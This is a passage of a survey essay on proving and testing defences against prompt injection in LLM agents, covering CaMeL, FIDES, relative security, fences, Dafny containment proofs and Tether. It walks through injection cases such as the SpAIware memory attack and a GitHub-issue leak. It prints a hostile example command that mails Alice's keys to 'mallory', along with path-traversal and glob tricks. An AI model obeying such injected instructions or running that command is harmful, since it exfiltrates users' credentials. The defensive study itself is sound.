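The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* cites the system card's finding that Opus 5 also resisted every attack in 129 tests of an agent using a web browser. If those tests were a random sample of what an attacker might try, the result would imply a failure rate below about 2.3%. In September, Anthropic described another model, Mythos 5.1, as its most robust so far on the external benchmark.

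Progress has been uneven. In June, Anthropic reported that Mythos 5 had achieved the best result yet on Gray Swan's benchmark, but that its safety scores in coding and computer use fell between those of two earlier models. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* found that the model and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking injections, and criticized Anthropic for reporting this quietly beneath a reassuring headline. Both accounts can be true, because a model can improve on one benchmark and get worse on another.

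Developers have not claimed to guarantee protection against prompt injection. OpenAI stated in December 2025 that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" (quoted by Narisetty and colleagues). Anthropic wrote of Opus 4.5 that determined attackers with enough time would probably do better than its tests suggested. Even Anthropic's Boris Cherny, who was enthusiastic about Opus 5, called it only "very hard to prompt inject successfully" (quoted in Willison, 2026). In *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*, Poireault (2026) reports that security researcher Ariel Fogel attributes the problem to the well-known lack of a firm boundary between trusted and untrusted text.

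An attack with a low success rate can also compromise many agents. Anthropic points out that a single malicious page can attack every agent that reads it, without the attacker choosing a target. If a million agents read a page whose attack works 0.2% of the time, about 2,000 of them will follow its instructions.

### The case for guards that sometimes fail

These guards are still useful, even though adaptive attacks can break them. Many attackers copy recent attacks that worked and move on when they fail. PIGuard reduced the fixed attack's success rate on Gemini from 30% to zero, which would benefit an organisation that mostly faces copied attacks. Nasr and colleagues, who broke every defence they tried, still consider classifiers useful for blocking unsophisticated attacks. A failure rate of one in 500 may be acceptable for an agent that can only search public web pages, but an agent that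 can empty a bank account needs a stronger defence.

Model-based guards are also easy to adopt, because a classifier or a better-trained model works without a written policy. The owner of a general assistant may not know in advance which websites it will need to visit or whom it will need to email, and so can't easily write rules for it. PIGuard can greatly reduce the number of ordinary tasks an assistant completes, but PromptGuard and the prompting defences barely reduce the number Gemini completes. Training by the developer requires nothing extra from the owner, and it accounts for much of the recent improvement in Claude.

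The strongest argument for guards that rely on a language model is that some harms are very hard to express as rules. One of the attacker's goals in AgentDojo is to make a travel agent reserve the most expensive hotel in Paris. The user wants the agent to reserve hotels, so a rule can't simply forbid the tool, and a price limit stops only the worst cases. If the hidden text instead makes the agent recommend a bad hotel and leave the booking to the user, the agent makes no suspicious tool call. A rule-based guard would need an exact definition of honest advice. A model can learn from examples to detect some dishonest advice, though an attacker can still look for a kind it misses.

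## Proofs that limit where untrusted text can flow in an agent

Ordinary code can track which text came from a stranger and which values the agent has since computed from it, even though it can't tell honest advice from dishonest advice. Researchers have designed several agents around this kind of tracking and proved theorems about some of them. The theorems limit the damage that injected instructions can do even if the model obeys them.

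### Writing the program before reading the email

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed splitting an agent between two language models. A privileged model can call tools but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools, so an email that hijacks it can't make it send anything.

The email can still corrupt the quarantined model's answers. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an agent that asks the quarantined model to write a reply based on a stranger's email and the user's private notes. If the email contains an instruction to quote the notes and the model follows it, the agent sends the notes to the stranger.

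CaMeL, a design by Debenedetti and others at Google DeepMind (2025), adds labels that record where each value came from. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) welcomed it as an exception to years of alarmingly little progress.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, work through an email task in the CaMeL style. Alice asks her agent to find Bob's latest email and send him a reminder about their meeting. An attacker has added a postscript to the email, asking for a cancellation note instead. An ordinary agent, which read the email in the same conversation in which it chose its tool calls, sent the cancellation. A CaMeL-style agent handles the task differently:

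1. The privileged model, or planner, receives Alice's request and a list of tools, but not the email. It writes a short program:

```
email  = get_last_email()
sender = ask_quarantined_model("Find the sender's address.", email)
send_email(to=sender, subject="Meeting reminder",
           body="Are you still free for our meeting?")
```

2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the first line and labels the email untrusted.
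3. On the second line, the quarantined model reads the email and returns an address. The interpreter labels the address untrusted too, because it came from an untrusted email.
4. Before the third line sends anything, the interpreter checks the labels against a policy. Here the policy requires a trusted subject and body. Both come from the planner's program, so the call goes ahead.

The postscript can't affect the wording, because the planner wrote the subject and body before the agent opened the email. It could still make the quarantined model return the wrong address and send the reminder to somebody else. A stricter policy would also require a trusted recipient, but then the agent couldn't take Bob's address from his email. According to TechSpot, CaMeL can ask the user to confirm a doubtful call instead of blocking it.

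Labels usually have two parts. One records whether an attacker could have influenced the value, and the other records who may learn it. A value computed from several others inherits all their restrictions, so adding one untrusted word to a trusted sentence makes the whole sentence untrusted. The second part can be "public" or "secret", or a list of permitted readers. If one document is open to Ann and Bea and another to Bea and Carl, a summary of both is open only to Bea.

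### Choosing one step at a time

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft design that keeps the ordinary agent loop, in which the planner chooses each tool call after receiving the last result. FIDES labels the whole conversation untrusted as soon as untrusted text enters it. A policy can then forbid any call with serious consequences, such as sending email to an outside address.

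That alone would make the agent almost useless after it read its first email. FIDES therefore hides a tool result in a variable whenever the result would worsen the conversation's label. The planner receives only the variable's name, which it can pass to another tool without reading the contents. To learn something about the contents, the planner can query a quarantined model whose answer must fit a fixed format, such as yes or no. An attacker who controls a yes-or-no answer can influence what the planner does next but can't use the answer to give it a new instruction.

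This flexibility matters for tasks whose steps depend on what the agent reads. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if the same sequence of tool calls and the same final response would solve it whatever the data. A request to "complete the tasks due today in my TODO app" isn't data-independent, because the agent has to read the list to find out which tools it needs. A CaMeL program can contain branches, but the planner has to write every branch in advance.

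Garby and colleagues point out that FIDES's guarantee for secrets covers data that the agent copies into a message, but not what an attacker can infer from the path the agent takes. Suppose an agent sends a stranger "yes" if the user's bank balance is above $10,000 and "no" otherwise. The stranger can then infer whether the balance is above $10,000, even though the message contains no part of it.

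### Two leaks in CaMeL

CaMeL's normal mode has the same gap. Dongol proved that labels like CaMeL's fail to stop a leak if the plan branches on the quarantined model's answer and then sends a different public constant from each branch. CaMeL also has a strict mode, which labels values according to the conditions that control them.

Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter can still miss a leak when a program skips a branch. A program of the kind they describe looks like this, where the balance is secret and everything else starts out public:

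```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(...)
```

Here are the two possible runs:

| Lines | Balance above $10,000 | Balance of $10,000 or less |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp = True`, `rich = True` | Both variables are true and public | Both variables are true and public |
| `if balance > 10000: tmp = False` | `tmp` becomes false and secret | Skipped, so `tmp` stays true and public |
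| `if tmp: rich = False` | Skipped, so `rich` stays true and public | `rich` becomes false and stays public |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | The email goes out | No email goes out |

When the interpreter decides whether to send the email, `rich` is public in both runs, so the check passes. But the email goes out only if the balance is above $10,000. The mistake is in the second row of the right-hand column, where skipping the assignment leaves `tmp` labeled "public" even though its value depends on the balance as much as it does in the other run.

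A program can repeat the trick any number of times. If it changes the threshold each time, 20 yes-or-no answers would be enough to find any whole-dollar balance up to about a million dollars, since 2^20 is 1,048,576.

The other leak comes from how CaMeL recovers from errors. If a program fails, CaMeL gives the planner the error message and has it write a new program. This retry loop is outside the interpreter, so each new program starts with clean labels even though the planner wrote it in response to an earlier failure. Suppose a program fails only when the user's account is overdrawn. If the planner's second attempt sends an email that the first would not have sent, anyone who receives it can learn that the account is overdrawn. Each run can leak one bit this way, namely whether it failed. CaMeL's developers knew about the problem and censor the error messages, but the retry still reveals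 to the planner that something went wrong.

A stranger can't easily exploit either leak by email, because the planner writes the programs without reading the email. An attacker would need a compromised planner, or one that happened to write a program whose structure allowed the leak. The leaks matter mainly because they show that reasonable-looking labelling rules can contain errors that are hard to notice. Garby and colleagues found another error that an uncompromised planner could trigger much more easily. If a program inserted an untrusted value into text, as in "Dear {name}", CaMeL's interpreter treated the result as trusted.

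### A language with a theorem

The CaMeL paper contained no proof but called formalization a "crucial direction" for further work. Garby and colleagues took this up by designing the LLMbda calculus, a very small programming language whose programs can hold conversations with a language model. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built out of functions.

Every value in the language has a label, and so does the conversation. A program can send a prompt and receive a reply, which takes on the label of the conversation that produced it. It can also clear the conversation's history, or fork the conversation, which means working in a temporary copy that is then discarded. These operations are enough to build a quarantined model. The program forks the conversation, clears the copy, asks about the untrusted email in the copy, and returns to the original conversation with only the answer.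 The email never enters the main conversation, and the answer carries an untrusted label.

The interpreter also keeps a label for the program's current position. This label is secret inside any branch whose condition depends on a secret. While it is secret, the interpreter stops the program from adding messages to a public conversation, a check that CaMeL omitted. Relabelling the conversation as secret wouldn't be enough, because the conversation would stay public in a run that skipped the branch, and that difference would reveal the secret.

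Stopping a program can reveal a secret, since an observer may notice that it never finished. The theorem therefore permits leaks only through whether a program finishes. It has to be a version of noninterference for programs with random results, because a language model can answer the same prompt in different ways.

Take an observer who may look only at public values. Let μ(q) be the probability that the program finishes with a result that looks like q to this observer when the secret has one value, and let ν(q) be the same probability when the secret has another value. The theorem says that there are numbers ω(q), adding up to at most 1, such that

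μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q.

An example shows what this allows. Suppose that when the secret is 0, the program always finishes, with "yes" 60% of the time and "no" 40% of the time. The theorem then rules out one of these two behaviours when the secret is 1:

| Behaviour when the secret is 1 | "Yes" | "No" | Doesn't finish | Smallest possible total for ω |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Allowed | 50% | 40% | 10% | 60% + 40% = 100% |
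| Ruled out | 50% | 50% | 0% | 60% + 50% = 110% |

In the allowed case, the two behaviours could become identical if the program finished more often. Garby and colleagues also proved that the leak, measured as half the sum of the absolute differences between μ and ν, is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. In the allowed case, the leak and the average are both 5%. A program that always finishes leaks nothing, because the average is zero.

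The same theorem also covers untrusted text if the observer sees only trusted values and the attacker's email replaces the secret. For Alice's reminder, this means that no change to Bob's email can influence a subject or body that passes the check for trusted text. The theorem doesn't protect the recipient's address, which is labeled untrusted.

Garby and colleagues checked the theorem in Lean. They also wrote the interpreter in Lean and proved that it produces results with the probabilities given by the language's definition, provided the model's replies follow the assumed distribution. The theorem holds whatever a hijacked model writes, even if the agent runs the reply as code. But it simplifies by treating the sources of data as part of the program. Whoever builds the tools must also label their results correctly and put a check on every tool that could do harm.

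The designers also had to find another way to handle retries, because in the language a failed attempt on real data would leave its label on everything that followed. Their agent therefore practises on made-up data first. In practice mode, tools that would change something, such as one that sends money, do nothing, and every file contains the same placeholder text. Once the practice program works, the planner writes a final version, and only that version touches real data.

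### Exceptions to the labels

Strict labels rule out some reasonable tasks. For example, an agent might sort incoming email into categories and put the category in the subject line of its reply. The category comes from a stranger's email, so it is untrusted, and the tool blocks it from being sent. Garby and colleagues added an operation called `endorse`, which lets a program declare an untrusted value trusted.

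If there are only eight categories, an attacker who controls the choice gains at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits of influence, and can't write the subject line. The program has to endorse the value before testing whether it is on the list, because testing an untrusted value would make everything inside the resulting branch untrusted, including the result of the endorsement. For the same reason, an attacker gains nothing by getting the agent to run code that contains `endorse`, as long as that code is still labelled untrusted.

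Garby and colleagues proved that endorsement can't be used to reveal secrets, but it necessarily weakens the protection against untrusted influence. The bound of log₂ n bits rests on an informal argument, and it doesn't help with an account number or a payment amount, which can't come from a short list. If Alice asks her agent to pay the bill described in a file, the planner has to endorse whatever account number the file contains, so an attacker who can replace the file receives the payment. The advantage over an unlabelled agent is that the endorsement appears in the program, where a person or another tool can find it before the program runs.

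### Comparing an agent with one that never obeys

Dongol starts from a different problem. Noninterference rejects agents that disclose information on purpose. For example, Alice may want her agent to send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. The agent's reply then depends on her private data, so it violates noninterference even though the agent is doing what she wants. She could write a policy listing what the agent may release, but she would need a new one for each task.

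Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent whose model never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The two agents are otherwise identical. They run the same plan, which is fixed before either reads any untrusted text, and the same runtime monitor allows or denies each call.

Two runs of an agent form a leak if Alice's secrets differ, the attacker sends the same text in both, and the attacker observes different results. The agent is relatively secure if, whenever it has a leak between secrets σ₁ and σ₂, the reference agent also has a leak between σ₁ and σ₂. The attacker may use a different email to get it. Dongol's two main examples show why this matters:

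| Injected instruction | What the real agent reveals | Could any email make the reference agent reveal it? | Counts as a leak? |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Send your calendar" | Alice's calendar | Yes, a genuine meeting request | No |
| "Also include the reset code" | A password-reset code | No | Yes |

In the calendar example, the model obeys the attacker, but the attacker gains nothing because an honest request for a meeting would have produced the same calendar. By contrast, an attacker can get the reset code only through an injection, because the code is in the agent's memory for another task and the plan never sends it.

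The definition accepts some injections that reveal much more than the agent's task requires. Suppose an agent's job is to tell callers whether a guess at a four-digit PIN is right, and an injection makes it reveal the whole PIN. For any two PINs, guessing one of them would make the reference agent answer differently depending on which PIN is real. The definition therefore accepts the injection, even though a caller might need thousands of guesses to learn as much from an honest agent. Dongol noticed this and defined a stricter, uniform version, in which the reference agent's email must be chosen without knowledge of the secrets. A fixed guess of 1234 can't distinguish 5555 from 6666, so the injection counts as a leak under the uniform version.

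### Where to put the fence

Dongol and others originally developed relative security to analyse Spectre. The usual defence against Spectre is a barrier that stops the processor from continuing past a check before the check finishes. The equivalent for an agent is a fence, which removes certain tools once untrusted text may have reached the model.

The position of the fence makes a large difference. In the next examples, the agent reads a stranger's email and a secret, and the plan contains a lock that removes the Send tool for the rest of the run:

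| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected call could send |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read the email, read the secret, lock | The secret |
| Middle | Read the email, lock, read the secret | Anything already in the agent's memory |
| Early | Lock, read the email, read the secret | Nothing |

Private data can still leak with the middle fence, even though the agent loses Send before it gets the secret. The agent may already have private data from an earlier session, and the model may follow the email's instructions immediately after reading them, while Send is still available. Only the early fence leaves no gap between reading the email and losing Send.

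Dongol's fence theorem generalises this. Every plan is relatively secure, whatever text the model treats as an instruction, if these conditions hold:

- The monitor removes every tool that an injection could call, no later than the first time the agent reads untrusted text, and never gives those tools back.
- Each injected instruction leads to a single tool call.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. The contents of an injected call may depend on secrets, but its timing may not.
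- The attacker observes the contents and order of the calls that the monitor allows, but not their timing or any refusals.

In the proof, the monitor silently denies every injected call, so the attacker observes exactly what the reference agent would have produced. The result therefore also satisfies the uniform version of relative security. The theorem applies to runs that end. For an agent that runs forever, it also requires that the model not go on obeying injected instructions forever, because then the plan would never continue.

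An agent that handles one email after another will eventually need its tools back. The monitor should return them only when the model starts a fresh session, because returning them while the previous email is still in the conversation reopens the leak. Even a new session can contain untrusted text if it loads long-term memory. In the SpAIware attack, a web page or document got ChatGPT to save an instruction in its long-term memory. ChatGPT then loaded the instruction in later conversations and sent the user's messages to the attacker. Dongol modelled this attack and proved that a fence fails if it treats the memory as trusted. The theorem applies again if the monitor treats the memory as untrusted text.

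Some of the theorem's other conditions are also easy to break in practice. For instance, it requires refusals to be silent, and they aren't if the attacker can read error messages. The theorem covers only single calls, so an injected program could copy the secret into a value that the plan later sends, and the plan's own permitted call would leak it. To prevent this, the agent has to run injected programs in a sandbox that discards their changes, and the fence has to cover reading as well as sending.

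### Approving a tool and approving a call

Many agents ask their users for permission before acting, which lets the agents keep access to a tool like Send after reading untrusted text. Whether this is safe depends on exactly what the user approves. Suppose Alice's agent shows her a reply, "Tuesday works", and she approves it. If her approval means "the agent may use Send once", an injected instruction can make the agent send her private data to the attacker first. The monitor then blocks her own reply because the approval has already been used.

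If the user approves the exact call, Send("Tuesday works"), the monitor denies any injected call with different text. The attacker can make the agent send the approved reply early, but can't change it. Dongol proved this arrangement secure for every injection that calls Send, as long as the model doesn't follow the injected instructions forever and the attacker can't measure time.

An attacker who can measure when the reply arrives may learn a little. Suppose the injection tries to send a private note. If the note says "Tuesday works", the monitor allows the call and the reply arrives one step early. Otherwise, it arrives at the normal time. The attacker therefore learns whether the note matches the reply. This is rarely worth much, but it could matter if there were only a few possible notes.

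### Twenty-five agents

Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, gives verdicts on 25 small agents, each built to isolate one mechanism. The definitions and proofs take up about 31,600 lines in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant. Claude Code helped generate the proofs, and Isabelle checked them all.

Some verdicts, such as the one for the early fence, hold for every injection, but others cover only the attack in the example. The calendar agent is secure against "send your calendar", but an attacker could try a different instruction, and the reset code example shows what happens if the agent has something else worth stealing. A "secure" verdict from this list therefore doesn't prove that a product with a similar design is secure.

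Delimiters and similar marks around untrusted text fail the test whatever marks the developer chooses. This follows almost directly from the set-up, in which the attacker decides how the model reads marked text. Marking therefore can't provide a guarantee without an assumption about the model. The attack experiments suggest the same.

CaMeL-style labels can block harmless actions along with harmful ones. In one of Dongol's examples, the quarantined model drafts a reply using a stranger's email and Alice's private notes, and the monitor stops the agent from sending anything labelled private. This is secure however the quarantined model behaves, but only because the agent can never send the reply. A draft that doesn't quote the notes gets the same private label as one that does.

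### Agents and harms outside the proofs

Dongol's theorems don't apply to the ordinary agent loop, in which the agent decides on each call after reading the result of the last one. Such an agent has no fixed plan, so there is no reference agent to compare it with. FIDES keeps this loop and can still enforce its label policies, though its guarantee for secrets is weaker.

The theorems also exclude tools whose reply depends on the query. If an attacker runs a search engine that the agent uses, the attacker can read each query, which may contain private data, before choosing the reply. Dongol's model lets the attacker choose what the agent reads, but not in response to a particular call. This is a large gap because agents that search the web make such calls all the time.

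An injection can also do harm without revealing anything, such as by making an agent delete files or book the most expensive hotel in Paris. Relative security doesn't cover such actions, because the attacker learns nothing from them. The theorem about the LLMbda calculus covers some of them, since it guarantees that untrusted text can't influence any value that a tool requires to be trusted. But if Alice asks for a hotel based on online reviews, the choice has to depend on text that strangers wrote, so this guarantee can't apply to it.

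The most common drawback is probably lost usefulness. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, quoted in Willison (2025), acknowledges that its patterns deliberately prevent agents from "solving arbitrary tasks". Relative security can't measure this loss, because the reference agent has the same restrictions. A monitor that denies every call passes the test, so developers have to check separately that the agent still does its job.

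One of the real attacks that Dongol modelled shows that a defence can also block useful work. A user asked an agent to look at the open issues in a public GitHub repository. One issue contained hidden instructions, and the agent published data from the user's private repositories in a pull request, which is a proposed change that anyone can read. A fence that stops the agent from opening pull requests prevents the attack. But the user may have wanted the agent to fix the issues, and the normal way to propose a fix is to open a pull request.

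## Proofs about the software that carries out an agent's actions

A restriction like the one in the GitHub example depends on knowing when a stranger's text may have reached the model. Another kind of proof doesn't require knowing this. It assumes that the model might request any action at any time, and shows that the software around the model carries out only the permitted ones.

### A model that may request anything

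Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, wrote such a proof in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier. Slightly simplified, the model appears in their program like this:

```
method {:extern} GetActionFromLLM(c: Constants, v: Variables)
    returns (action: Action)
```

The method has no body, so the verifier can assume nothing about its result except that it has the type `Action`, which is a fixed list of the kinds of thing the agent can request. Any proof about the surrounding code must therefore hold for every possible action, so it still applies if the model is hijacked or the developer switches to a different one.

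The proof compares an abstract description, which sets out the permitted behaviour, with a concrete description of the software's main loop. Each responds to an action with an event, such as reading a file, or with a "no effect" event if it refuses the request. The argument has three steps:

1. The two descriptions start in matching states.
2. If they are in matching states and the concrete one responds to an action, the abstract one can respond to the same action with a matching event, and they end in matching states again.
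3. If the abstract response obeys the policy, so does the concrete response that matches it.

Steps 1 and 2 ensure that the abstract and concrete descriptions match throughout any sequence of actions. Dafny also proves that the abstract description always obeys the policy, so by step 3 the concrete description does too.

Moon and Varshney applied this to PocketFlow, a roughly 100-line framework for building agents. Its list has four kinds of action, and the policy has three rules. The agent may read files only inside one folder, may call only tools on an approved list, and must stop after a fixed number of steps. If the folder is `/work` and instructions injected through an email make the model request `/home/alice/keys`, the loop produces a "no effect" event and reads nothing.

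This policy restricts which tools the agent calls but not what it does with them, so an agent with an approved email tool could send anything in the folder to anyone. The folder rule may also be weaker than it sounds. In the published theorem, a path counts as inside the folder if it starts with the folder's name. The path `/work/../home/alice/keys` starts with `/work`, but `..` means "go up one level", so it leads to Alice's keys. Unless other code resolves such paths first, the agent could read the keys and the theorem would still hold.

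The trusted base includes the policy, the Dafny tools, and the code that turns the model's text into an action. It also includes the assumption that the agent has no other way to affect the outside world, so Moon and Varshney recommend running the whole system in a sandbox. They argue that a more capable model can't weaken the guarantee. That is true of the listed actions, but such a model may be better at finding bugs in the unproved software underneath, or at doing harm with actions the policy allows.

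### The action that contains all the others

Suppose the developer adds an action called `RunCommand`, which takes any line of text and runs it as a command. Coding agents commonly have one. An injected instruction can then make the model request this:

```
cat /home/alice/keys | mail mallory
```

The command reads Alice's keys and emails them to Mallory. The framework records only one event, "ran a command", with no file read outside `/work` and no call to an unapproved tool, so every rule still holds and the theorem is still true.

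The developer could ban commands that mention `/home/alice`, but `cat /home/al*/keys` would still open `/home/alice/keys`. A command can also start a script that assembles the file's name as it runs. Rice's theorem shows that no algorithm can work out, in general, what arbitrary programs will do. Moon and Varshney acknowledge that with an action this general, the guarantee is only as strong as whatever restricts the command.

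### Watching what a command does

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) handles arbitrary commands by running them and observing what they do, rather than by reading their text. It runs each command on a disposable layer over the file system and holds its network requests at a proxy. It also records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the kernel. From these, a component called Isolate infers a series of simple actions, such as "copy this file" or "upload that one". If the policy allows all of the actions, Tether applies the changes to the real files and releases the network requests. Otherwise it discards both.

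Tether also keeps a label for each file. Suppose a user lets an agent upload status reports to an outside site, but not the company's inventory, `servers.csv`:

| Command | Label of `report.txt` afterwards | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Upload `report.txt` | Public | Allow |
| Copy `servers.csv` to `report.txt` | Sensitive | Allow |
| Upload `report.txt` | Sensitive | Deny |

The two uploads are identical, so a guard that judged each command on its own would have to treat them alike. Copying the inventory through several temporary files doesn't help the attacker, because each copy keeps the label.

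Lean proofs cover the part of Tether that applies the policy. For example, they show that adding a permissive rule can't override a refusal, and that a refused action leaves the labels unchanged. Sistla and colleagues also proved seven properties of the 24-rule policy they used in their experiments. One is that secret data never enters the agent's context if none was there at the start. These proofs hold for any number of actions.

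Isolate has no proof, and if it misses a copy, the proved part will apply the rules correctly to the wrong labels. Sistla and colleagues fuzzed it with random chains of file operations, carrying out each operation by a randomly chosen method, and compared the labels and verdicts with the correct ones. They also had a language model attack the whole system in ten tasks. The model's success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions as they fixed the gaps, including one involving hard links, which give a file a second name. Ten tasks in one simple environment are too few to show that no gaps remain.

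McCann (2026), in *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, describes a similar division in a commercial system for running agents. The proofs are about an abstract model, and random tests compare the running software with its specification. The 188th random input exposed a bug in the permission code that the developer's ordinary tests had missed.

To measure Tether's performance, Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs of coding agents, some of which had a harmful side task. These results cover only runs whose actions Tether can model, which excludes those that use databases or background processes:

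| Guard | Harmful runs blocked (of 344) | Harmless runs blocked (of 1,590) |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 | 74 |
| Auto Mode, a model-based guard in Claude Code | 315 | 155 |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy in its instructions | 307 | 55 |

Tether's perfect score probably overstates its strength. The attacks were recordings, so the attacker could not adapt to Tether. The researchers had also refined the policy by trying drafts on benchmark runs, so the benchmark was not an independent test of it. In 17 of the 74 false alarms, the agent had read secret or sensitive files, often through a broad search that opened every file on the disk. Tether can't detect whether the agent used the contents, so it treats them as used.

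### Checking the plan before it runs

Tether checks each action as it arrives. Like the guards in Schneider's theory, it can stop a harmful step but can't make the agent finish its job. A guard that has the whole plan in advance can also check for missing steps. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) adds such a check to CaMeL, whose planner writes a program before the agent reads any untrusted text. CaMeLoT turns the program into a finite-state model and passes it to a model checker before any tool runs.

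Their main example is an agent that responds to security alerts and can isolate a suspect computer from the network. Two of its rules are:

always (isolate a computer → approval already requested)

always (open a ticket → eventually resolve or escalate it)

A runtime guard could enforce the rule about approval by blocking the isolation. But if the agent has already carried out a long investigation, that work may be wasted, whereas CaMeLoT finds the missing step at the start. The rule about tickets concerns completion. A plan that opens a ticket and then ends breaks this rule, although every step in it is harmless. CaMeLoT reports the faulty path to the planner, which tries to repair the plan. (*LEANGUARD*, a similar project, can make some repairs without the model. According to *LEANGUARD* (2026), Lean searches for a call close to the refused one that keeps the user's intent, and proves that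 the rules allow it.)

These rules promise less than their names suggest. The approval rule checks that the plan asks for approval, not that anyone grants it. The ticket rule ensures that every path includes a closing step, but the ticket service could still fail. CaMeLoT also ignores the conditions in a program and treats each `if` as a free choice, so it would reject this safe plan:

```
if false_alarm:
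    resolve(ticket)
if not false_alarm:
    escalate(ticket)
```

Every real run closes the ticket, but the model includes a path that skips both steps. Rewriting the second condition as an `else` would remove that path.

CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans in one test. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote each plan to break a particular rule, so the test shows that the checks work but doesn't measure how often agents write unsafe plans. On the AgentDojo benchmark, CaMeLoT could fully reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies. Most of the other six depend on facts available only at run time, such as who can read a shared file.

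### Checking an effect against the request

*Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* (Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler, 2026) proposes checking that each effect is what somebody asked for, because a permitted action can still be wrong. Its example is a disk driver written by an AI that may be hostile. The kernel asks the driver to write eight blocks of data starting at block 100, and the driver tries to write them at block 200. An ordinary permission check would allow this because both addresses are legal. In the proposed design, the driver can only suggest a command, and a trusted mediator holds the kernel's original request. The mediator compares the two addresses and refuses the command before anything reaches the disk.

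Hu and colleagues have not yet built the mediator or proved anything about it. The method also needs a request with an exact meaning, like a kernel's, rather than one like "sort out my meetings."

### When a rule depends on a detector

Some rules depend on a classifier that can be wrong. Suppose an agent may not send text to an outside service if it draws on any confidential message. It wants to send a summary of two messages, and a classifier puts the probability that they are confidential at 45% and 25%. A guard that treats anything below 50% as safe will clear both messages and allow the call. But the probability that at least one of them is confidential is higher. If the two are independent, it is

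1 − 0.55 × 0.75 ≈ 59%.

If they are never both confidential, it is 45% + 25% = 70%, the worst case.

*Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues, 2026) describes a method that blocks an action when an upper bound on the risk exceeds a threshold. The bound holds however the errors are related. An exact calculation would be too slow for a long run, so the method uses a faster one that may overestimate the risk but never underestimates it.

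This guarantee assumes that an attacker can't change the detector's error rate. Solko-Breslin and colleagues suggest that the assumption is reasonable if the detector reads only trusted inputs or resists manipulation. It would fail for the classifiers in Nasr and colleagues' experiments, because the attackers searched for text that the classifiers would misjudge.

### Where the rules come from

One source of rules is hazard analysis, which engineers use in aviation. Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, apply it to a calendar agent. A user books a medical appointment that clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and emails a colleague, Bob, to explain, naming the treatment in the subject line. No attacker is involved. The analysis starts from the people affected and works towards a rule:

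1. The user values privacy.
2. The corresponding loss is the disclosure of private information.
3. The agent could cause this loss by putting details of one event into an email about another.
4. So each email must exclude anything private to people other than its recipient.

The other people at the meeting want to be told about changes, so one rule requires the agent to email all of them after every change. A guard can enforce the privacy rule only if the appointment is labeled private, so Doshi and colleagues propose that tools supply such labels with their data.

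Hong, She and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety*, reviewed 80 benchmarks for agent safety and security and found that 61% stated no requirements for the agent's behaviour and 24% gave only vague goals, such as refusing "anything unsafe". In three benchmarks with more definite policies, ordinary code could enforce 74% of the requirements, and 95% of those needed only simple checks. For example, an airline's software can refuse to cancel a flight that the passenger has already taken. All three benchmarks were for agents with narrow jobs, so the 74% figure would probably be lower for a general assistant.

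Rules also change, and a more generous rule can break a task that used to work. Shivakumar, Priya and Gao (2026), in *Agenra*, give an example in which an agent has two permissions, and the software uses the first one that fits:

| Permissions, in order | Delete A, then B | Delete A twice |
|---|---|---|
| Delete B once; delete A once | Works | Refused |
| Delete A or B once; delete A once | B refused | Works |

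After the change, deleting A uses up the wider permission and leaves none for B. Agenra checks such changes with proofs in Lean, but it can't supply a rule that the developer forgot. In a test of 51 changes that the researchers wrote, it approved all 21 that preserved the existing tasks and none of the 30 that broke one.

Language models can also draft the rules. Sistla and colleagues had a model propose and revise Tether's policy. In CaMeLoT, a model fills in a fixed set of templates to identify what the user's request requires, and ordinary code turns them into formulas. The model identified exactly the right set of required actions for 85 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks. Translation can be much less reliable when it is less constrained. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) cites a benchmark in which only 25% to 34% of models' translations into a formal planning language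 had the right meaning.

### A rule about an empty list

Moon and Varshney used AI to write their specifications and proofs, and they report a failure that their checks missed. Each result had to pass three checks before the final verification. The Dafny code had to be well formed, and the proof had to fail both when a tool removed most of its content and when a model planted a plausible error in it.

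One test used an agent that looks things up in documents and may read only those on an approved list. The AI had to work from a template with no field for documents, although it did have a list of tool calls and this rule:

every entry in `tool_calls` is in `allowed_tools`.

When the AI derived the rule without access to the agent's code, it recorded each document in `tool_calls`, so the rule applied to documents as if they were tool calls. When it could read the code, it noted that this agent had no list of approved tools and left `tool_calls` empty. The rule was then vacuously true, because an empty list has no entry that could break it, and it did not restrict which documents the agent read.

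Dafny verified both versions, and both passed all three checks. The checks altered the proof, but none tested whether the rule ever applied to anything. Moon and Varshney propose checking that the agent can reach a state in which the list has an entry. This check would have caught the mistake, but a list with one harmless entry would still pass it. They made only four runs, so the frequency of such failures is unknown. In *Pre-QED*, Lim, Tu and colleagues (2026) warn of a related problem in ordinary software, where people may trust a library labelled "verified" although its theorem covers only one sequence of calls.

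### Harms that no rule about actions can state

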